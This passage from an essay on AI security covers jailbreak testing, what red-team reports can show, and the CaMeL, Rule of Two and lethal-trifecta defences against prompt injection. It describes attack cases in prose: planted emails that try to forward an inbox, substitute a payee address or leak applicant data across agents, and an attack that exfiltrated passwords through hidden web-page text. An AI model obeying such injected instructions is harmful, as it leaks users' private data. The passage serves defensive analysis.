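|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.5 | 63 | 385 | $58 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 18 | 231 | $278 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0 | 0 | None found |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0 | 0 | None found |

An expert's combination was about 12 times as likely as a random one to break Grok, and about 26 times as likely to break Gemini. The experts didn't adjust their combinations to either model, so the gain came from general knowledge of which building blocks work.

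If the 1,000 combinations were a fair sample, the 3/n limit puts the share that work on Claude Fable 5 or GPT-5.6 Sol below 0.3%, but up to 300,000 of the 100 million combinations could still work. Timm and colleagues also left out every method that adjusts to a model's responses, the kind that broke the twelve defences. They present their test as a minimum standard. It identifies models that are easy to break, but a model that passes may still not be secure.

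### Does automated red teaming tell a company anything?

Schulhoff thinks most companies learn nothing from automated red teaming because the result is predictable. All current language models can be broken, and almost any of the more than 2,000 automated tools will find thousands of prompts that do it. A vendor can use the alarming results to sell a guardrail. Schulhoff adds that a chatbot with no access to private data or tools can do little harm that users could not do with the underlying model directly. Schulhoff sees value in AI laboratories checking the worst their own models can do, but advises other companies to test how the model connects to their software, including its permissions.

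Schulhoff runs contests and sells courses and expert red teaming, so the argument also helps that business compete with automated rivals. But the experiments by Nasr and colleagues support much of the argument. If a tool can break nearly any system in a few dozen attempts, you learn little from a report that it broke yours.

Automated tools do not always succeed, however. The evolutionary search failed on a quarter of its cases against an undefended GPT-5 Mini. The random search by Timm and colleagues found dozens of universal jailbreaks for one model and none for another. Differences this large can help a company choose between models, or show a developer which rivals have better safeguards.

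Automated tests can also cover many fields at once with the same effort in each, whereas people tend to concentrate on whatever is working. Timm and colleagues compared Grok 4.3 with its successor and found that the number of expert-made universal jailbreaks for biological weapons had fallen from ten to zero. In each of the other four fields, the newer model had as many or more. A company that tested only biology would have concluded that its safeguards had improved.

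That comparison is a form of regression testing, in which developers rerun old tests after each change to check that nothing has broken. Fixed lists of attacks work well for this, even though they overstate how strong a defence is. If an attack that a guardrail blocked last month now gets through, the developers know the guardrail has a weakness, but if it is still blocked, they know only that this attack does not work.

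Amazon researchers found a way to make Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 identify software vulnerabilities despite its safeguards. According to Anthropic's *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), a new classifier blocks that technique in over 99% of cases but also flags harmless coding requests more often. The 99% figure is good evidence that the company repaired the reported problem, but it does not measure how long an attacker would take to find a variation that works. At the end of June 2026, Anthropic knew of no universal jailbreak for the model and had opened a programme for researchers to report new jailbreaks.

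### What a red-team report can support

A report that says only "we found jailbreaks" or "we found none" supports almost no conclusion. A useful report describes the testers and gives their effort in hours, attempts or money. For example, the results of Anthropic's bounty could be reported as "testers made 198,000 attempts over 1,736 hours, and one of them found a serious failure". Readers can compare that with another system's figures if the questions and the definition of failure are similar.

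Whether an attack counts as a jailbreak can depend on the definition. SecurityWeek's *Anthropic Disputes Fable 5 AI Jailbreak* reports that a hacker announced a jailbreak shortly after Fable 5 launched, and that Anthropic said it was not a real one. Many of the strongest attacks reported in Anthropic's first bounty exploited the company's grading rather than getting around the classifiers, for example by producing long texts that collected points. Sharma and colleagues judged that these answers were much less useful than their scores suggested.

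To reduce such disputes, Anthropic has drafted a scale for jailbreaks that help with cyberattacks. It scores how much a jailbreak adds to what an attacker can already do, how many tasks it works on, how much skill it takes to use, and how easily others could find it. In one of its examples, a jailbreak leads a model to discover the Log4Shell flaw. This would have been serious in December 2021 but would score zero today, because every security scanner can find the flaw.

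The report should also list the categories the testers covered and those they left out. Sharma and colleagues studied a chatbot with ten set questions about weapons, which shows little about an agent that handles email. Nasr and colleagues left out systems such as CaMeL, which plan an agent's actions before it reads any untrusted text, because their attack could not succeed in most of the chosen cases. Davies notes that there has been much less progress on models with public weights, since an attacker can remove the guardrails.

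Finally, the testers should say whether they attacked the system that customers will use or only one part of it. During Anthropic's first bounty, one report seemed to describe a universal jailbreak. The cause was a programming error that let users receive up to 128 more tokens after the classifier had triggered a stop. The classifier had worked correctly, so testing it alone would have missed the problem.

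## CaMeL: limiting what an agent can do whatever it reads

The twelve defences that adaptive attackers broke all depended on how a model or a filter responded to text. CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind published in 2025, assumes that attackers may fool the model and limits what the agent can then do.

The developer of an email assistant can list its tools, the data each tool can reach and where that data may go, even though nobody can list every prompt that might reach the assistant. The safest approach is to assume that some text could make the model try to forward the inbox to a stranger, and to test whether the emails would be sent. Apache fixed Log4Shell in a similar way, by no longer evaluating lookups in logged text.

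### Two models and an interpreter

CaMeL builds on a design that the programmer Simon Willison (2023) proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. A privileged model can call tools but never reads text from strangers. A quarantined model reads that text but cannot call tools. CaMeL adds an interpreter, an ordinary program that runs code and checks each action. Willison's *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes the process:

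1. The privileged model receives the user's request, but no emails, web pages or files. It writes a short program in a restricted version of Python.
2. The interpreter runs the program line by line.
3. When a line requires someone to understand untrusted text, the interpreter passes the text to the quarantined model, which returns a value such as a name or a summary.
4. The interpreter tags each value with its source and with who may read it. A value that comes from other values inherits their tags.
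5. Before each tool call, the interpreter compares the tags with a policy, and then allows the call, refuses it or asks the user.

Suppose a user asks for a summary of today's emails, and one of them contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. The privileged model sees only the user's request and writes a program like this:

```
emails = get_emails(date="today")
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarise these emails", emails)
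show_user(summary)
```

The quarantined model may try to follow the injected instruction, but it can only return text. The program has no line that forwards email, and nothing in the emails can add one, so no wording of the instruction can get the inbox forwarded. The attacker can still change the summary.

Other programs need to send email. In Willison's example, the user asks the assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a reminder. An attacker who wrote that email could plant a different address, and the two-model design would send the reminder there. Debenedetti and colleagues pointed out this weakness in Willison's proposal. CaMeL tags the email as "untrusted", and the address taken from it gets the same tag. If the policy allows sending only to trusted recipients, the interpreter stops and asks the user.

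Writing the program in advance protects the control flow (the choice and order of actions), and the tags protect the data flow (the movement of values into those actions). The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) relates such tracking to information-flow control, a branch of computer security that dates back to the 1970s.

### Results on AgentDojo

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stops nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo, the benchmark of office tasks, while completing a comparable number of tasks. Later measurements also show that it stops nearly all the attacks, but they show a much larger drop in the number of tasks completed.

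In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) tested ten defences on 57 AgentDojo tasks in banking, workplace chat and travel. They then tried 389 combinations of a task and an injected instruction. A language model rewrote each injection over six rounds, and its only feedback was how often the earlier versions had worked.

| Model | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, CaMeL | Adaptive attacks succeed, no defence | Adaptive attacks succeed, CaMeL |
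|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 67% | 26% | 52.4% | 0% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 77% | 53% | 8.7% | 1.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 63% | 28% | 34.7% | 0.3% |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 89% | 39% | 16.5% | 0.5% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70% | 40% | 1.8% | 0.5% |

Rewriting the injections barely helped the attacker against CaMeL. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, 0.3% of attacks succeeded both with the benchmark's fixed wording and after rewriting. The filter PIGuard, by contrast, stopped every fixed attack on GPT-4o mini but let through 28% of the rewritten ones. Six rounds is a small search compared with the 800 attempts that Nasr and colleagues allowed. But a longer search would not help against CaMeL's program, because the privileged model wrote it before any model read the injection.

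All the successful attacks on CaMeL came from travel tasks. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) suggest this is because one of AgentDojo's travel attacks counts as successful if a certain text appears. An agent that quotes a hotel review word for word can therefore fail the test without having done anything wrong.

CaMeL reduced the share of completed tasks by between 25 and 51 percentage points. It also uses more computation. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that, in tests with GPT-4o, the median AgentDojo task took 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens with CaMeL as with no defence.

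### Why protected agents finish fewer tasks

Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks with its policy checks on and off. Turning the checks on reduced the share of tasks completed from 67% to 37.5% with GPT-5.2 and from 71% to 37.5% with MiMo-v2.5.

They also sorted the 144 pairs of a banking task and an attack into two groups. In 97, the attacker needs an action that the program for the user's task would never contain. For example, a program that summarises recent transactions has no line that sends money. Separating the two models is generally enough to stop these attacks. In the other 47, the program may already contain the action the attacker wants. If the user asks the assistant to pay the bill in a file, an attacker who can edit the file only needs to change the account number.

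Five of the 622 attacks that ran to completion succeeded with the policy checks off, and none of 588 did with the checks on. On these tasks, the policies halved CaMeL's usefulness to stop the less than 1% of attacks that succeeded without them. But the benchmark's attacks were fixed, and an adaptive attacker might have exploited the missing checks more often.

Two of the five successful attacks came from a request to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a program that went through those instructions and could call a different tool for each. A program fixed in advance limits an attacker only if it is narrow, and this one let the attacker reach any tool by writing in the file.

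Ma and colleagues found that requests like this are the most vulnerable to attack. On an undefended GPT-4o mini, adaptive attacks succeeded 79% of the time when the user left the choice of action to outside text, such as a to-do list on a web page, and 32% of the time when the user specified the action and all its details. But a system that keeps outside text from choosing the action also cannot carry out the to-do list.

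### Later systems

In tests by Ma and colleagues, two later defences reduced task completion less than CaMeL did. Progent limits an agent's tool calls to a policy based on the user's request, and ROPE accepts a sensitive value, such as a payee, only if it traces back to the user. On GPT-4o mini, Gemini 2.5 Flash and Claude Haiku 4.5, each defence reduced task completion by at most about seven percentage points, and no more than 7.7% of adaptive attacks succeeded. On a second benchmark with more open-ended tasks, GPT-4o mini completed 47% of tasks without a defence, 43% with ROPE and only 7% with Progent. Ma and several of the same colleagues also designed ROPE, so an independent test would be useful.

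Garby and colleagues looked for errors in CaMeL's own tracking and found several:

- Inserting an untrusted value into a fixed piece of text makes the result trusted. A program that builds an email address from a name in a stranger's message could therefore get past the check on recipients.
- CaMeL tags a variable as secret only when a line that depends on a secret changes it. If a program changes a variable only when an account balance is low, an unchanged variable reveals that the balance is high, but it carries no tag.
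- When a program fails, the privileged model sees an error message and writes a new program, and the tags start afresh. CaMeL censors these messages, but nobody has proved that the censoring is sufficient.

An attacker who cannot influence the program would find the second of these errors hard to exploit. The first could occur in ordinary programs.

Garby and colleagues built a small programming language for agents to avoid such errors. They used the proof checker Lean to prove that untrusted text cannot influence trusted values in any program in the language, except where the program explicitly accepts an untrusted value. The proof does not cover what an observer could learn from whether a program finishes. The guarantee holds whatever the model writes, so it applies to every possible prompt. But the proven property is narrow, and the developer still has to label every data source correctly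 and put a check on every sensitive tool.

Their agent tests each program on artificial data until it works, and only then runs it on the real account. With GPT-5.2, it completed 75% of the banking tasks. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay as instructed in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The program explicitly allowed payment details to come from that file. CaMeL's developers consider such cases outside the scope of its protection.

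*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applies the approach to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The plan can include clicking a button, but a model still has to find the button in an image that an attacker may control. An advertisement made to look like a cookie notice could trick the agent into clicking it. Extra checks blocked some versions of this attack, but another attack evaded even the strictest check.

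### Agents that call other agents

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, show that CaMeL's guarantee can fail when several protected agents work together. In their example, a user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. One agent queries the applicant database, a second coordinates the work, and a third sends messages. An attacker has planted an instruction in the database.

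The database agent and the coordinator handle the planted text only as data, so their programs do not change. But the coordinator includes the summary in its request to the messaging agent, which treats the request as coming from its user. The messaging agent's privileged model therefore trusts the planted instruction and writes a program that also emails the applicants' details to the attacker. A policy that trusts any address in the program would not catch this, because the privileged model wrote the attacker's address into the program.

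The fix is to send untrusted values through a separate channel, so that the receiving agent's privileged model never reads them. On a benchmark of multi-agent tasks, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with the separate channel. The benchmark's attacks rarely exploited the gap, so a tester who relied on the 0.2% figure could have missed it. Peters-Gill and colleagues found the gap by examining where trusted and untrusted text meet.

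### Testing the boundary without the model

A tester can check a boundary like this without writing any attack prompts. OWASP's *AI security testing*, a guide from a software security nonprofit, advises testers to send crafted tool calls directly to the layer that controls access. This bypasses the model, so a model refusal cannot hide a missing control. OWASP adds that a control found only in the model's instructions is not enforced against injection.

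Suppose an email assistant has ten tools, and its policy depends on three kinds of recipient, four sources of data and whether the user has approved the action. A tester can run all 10 × 3 × 4 × 2 = 240 cases in seconds. One run per case is enough because ordinary code makes the decision, and no judge has to interpret the result because the layer either carries out the call or refuses it. The tester can rely on these classes because the code is readable, as with Dijkstra's multiplier. The code that assigns a recipient to a class needs its own tests, since it might classify a lookalike address as a colleague's.

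Ma and Schmid (2026), in *SecureClaw*, report a test of this kind on their own system. SecureClaw stores protected data outside the agent and gives the model only a reference number and a short summary. Only a separate program, the executor, can act on the outside world. It acts only if the request exactly matches one that the policy has approved, so it refuses if an invoice's recipient changes after approval.

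Ma and Schmid assumed that an attacker had taken over the agent completely and could send the executor any request. They tried 25 forbidden requests, including ones with altered approvals, reused approvals or approvals from another session. The executor refused all 25 and accepted four legitimate requests. The legitimate requests matter because an executor that refused everything would also have stopped every attack. Twenty-five cases chosen by the designers can't be used to estimate a failure rate, but they do confirm that each check they exercise works.

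Such a test covers only the actions that pass through the boundary. If one tool can reach the email service directly, 240 correct refusals at the boundary do not stop emails sent through that tool. Apache's first Log4j repair failed this way. Ma and Schmid therefore recommend keeping a full inventory of the interfaces that can carry out external actions.

What an agent can read needs to be limited in the same way as what it can do. For an assistant that searches company documents, OWASP advises querying the search index with the credentials of different users. The test fails if the index returns a document that the user is not allowed to see, even if the model would have declined to quote from it.

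### The lethal trifecta and the rule of two

Some dangerous designs are visible from a list of tools. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, names three abilities that together let an attacker steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. The check for an email assistant might look like this:

| Tool | Reaches private data | Brings in strangers' text | Can send data out |
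|---|---|---|---|
| Read the inbox | Yes | Yes | No |
| Open a web page | No | Yes | Yes |
| Send an email | No | No | Yes |

This assistant would still be unsafe without the tool that sends email, because a request for a web page can carry stolen data in the address. The first two tools therefore already complete the trifecta. Willison warns that loading an image or showing the user a link to click can also leak data. One connector for the code-sharing site GitHub had all three abilities. It could read public comments that anyone might have written, open private code, and publish changes where others could see them.

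Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the idea into a design rule. Within one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties:

- It processes untrustworthy input.
- It has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change things or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three properties should not act without supervision, such as a person who approves its actions. The third property is broader than Willison's because it includes changes that send no data out, so the rule also covers an agent that an attacker tricks into deleting records.

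Meta gives three ways to apply the rule to an email assistant. The assistant can read only messages from trusted senders, work without access to private data, or send messages only to trusted recipients or after a person has checked the draft. An agent can also switch restrictions during a session. For instance, it can browse the web first, then lose its ability to communicate when it opens internal systems. The order matters because an injected instruction from the web may still be in the context window.

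An inspector can apply either rule in an afternoon, without running the model. But the answers have to be right, and it is easy to overlook a way for data to get out. Willison describes how the security firm PromptArmor attacked Google's programming tool Antigravity through instructions in tiny type on a web page. The agent collected passwords and code from the user's files, then sent them out by opening a malicious site in its own browser. The browser was an approved tool, and visiting a page is an ordinary use of it.

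The two rules are also less precise than CaMeL. They depend only on which abilities an agent has, while CaMeL allows all three abilities and checks where each value goes. CaMeL's extra precision requires a correct interpreter and correct policies.

### Policies, approvals and permitted harm

Debenedetti and colleagues list the need for people to write and update the policies among CaMeL's main drawbacks. They also warn of user fatigue, in which people who see too many approval requests start to accept them all. Meta likewise mentions users who confirm a warning without reading it. A strict policy that triggers constant requests could therefore protect less than a looser one that triggers few.

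On 10 February 2026, Schulhoff withdrew a criticism of CaMeL made in an earlier version of the argument against AI security products. Schulhoff had written that CaMeL fails whenever a task requires both reading and sending, because it grants permissions according to the user's request. An assistant asked for a summary would get permission only to read, but one asked to forward messages would get permission to read and send, and an injected instruction could misuse both. A note at the top of the passage says that this criticism mischaracterised the original CaMeL and that the attack does not work against it.

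In Schulhoff's example of forwarding the day's operational emails, CaMeL would take the recipient from the user's request, so an attacker's address would never reach the code that sends them. A smaller risk remains because the quarantined model decides which emails are operational. If it reads them all together, a planted message can influence its choice, and the recipient might get a private email or miss an important one.

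SecureClaw's remaining failures were also permitted actions with the wrong details. On AgentDojo, four of 629 attacks succeeded, compared with 31% when the agent had no defence. In three, the action was allowed but the attacker chose who it involved, and in the fourth the agent changed the wrong object. A more detailed policy might have stopped them, but it would have required more rules. Ma and Schmid do not claim that every action the policy allows is what the user wanted.

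Limiting an agent's actions also does little to prevent false or harmful text. If an attacker sends an email claiming that a supplier has a new bank account, the quarantined model may include the claim in its summary. If the user believes it and asks the assistant to pay the new account, the policy will probably allow the payment because the trusted request came from the user. Meta lists misinformation in an agent's answers among the harms that its rule does not prevent.

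CaMeL also does not address jailbreaks. It treats the user as trusted, so it does not stop a user who wants the model to write something dangerous. With a chatbot that has no tools, the harm is in the text itself, so CaMeL has no action to block.
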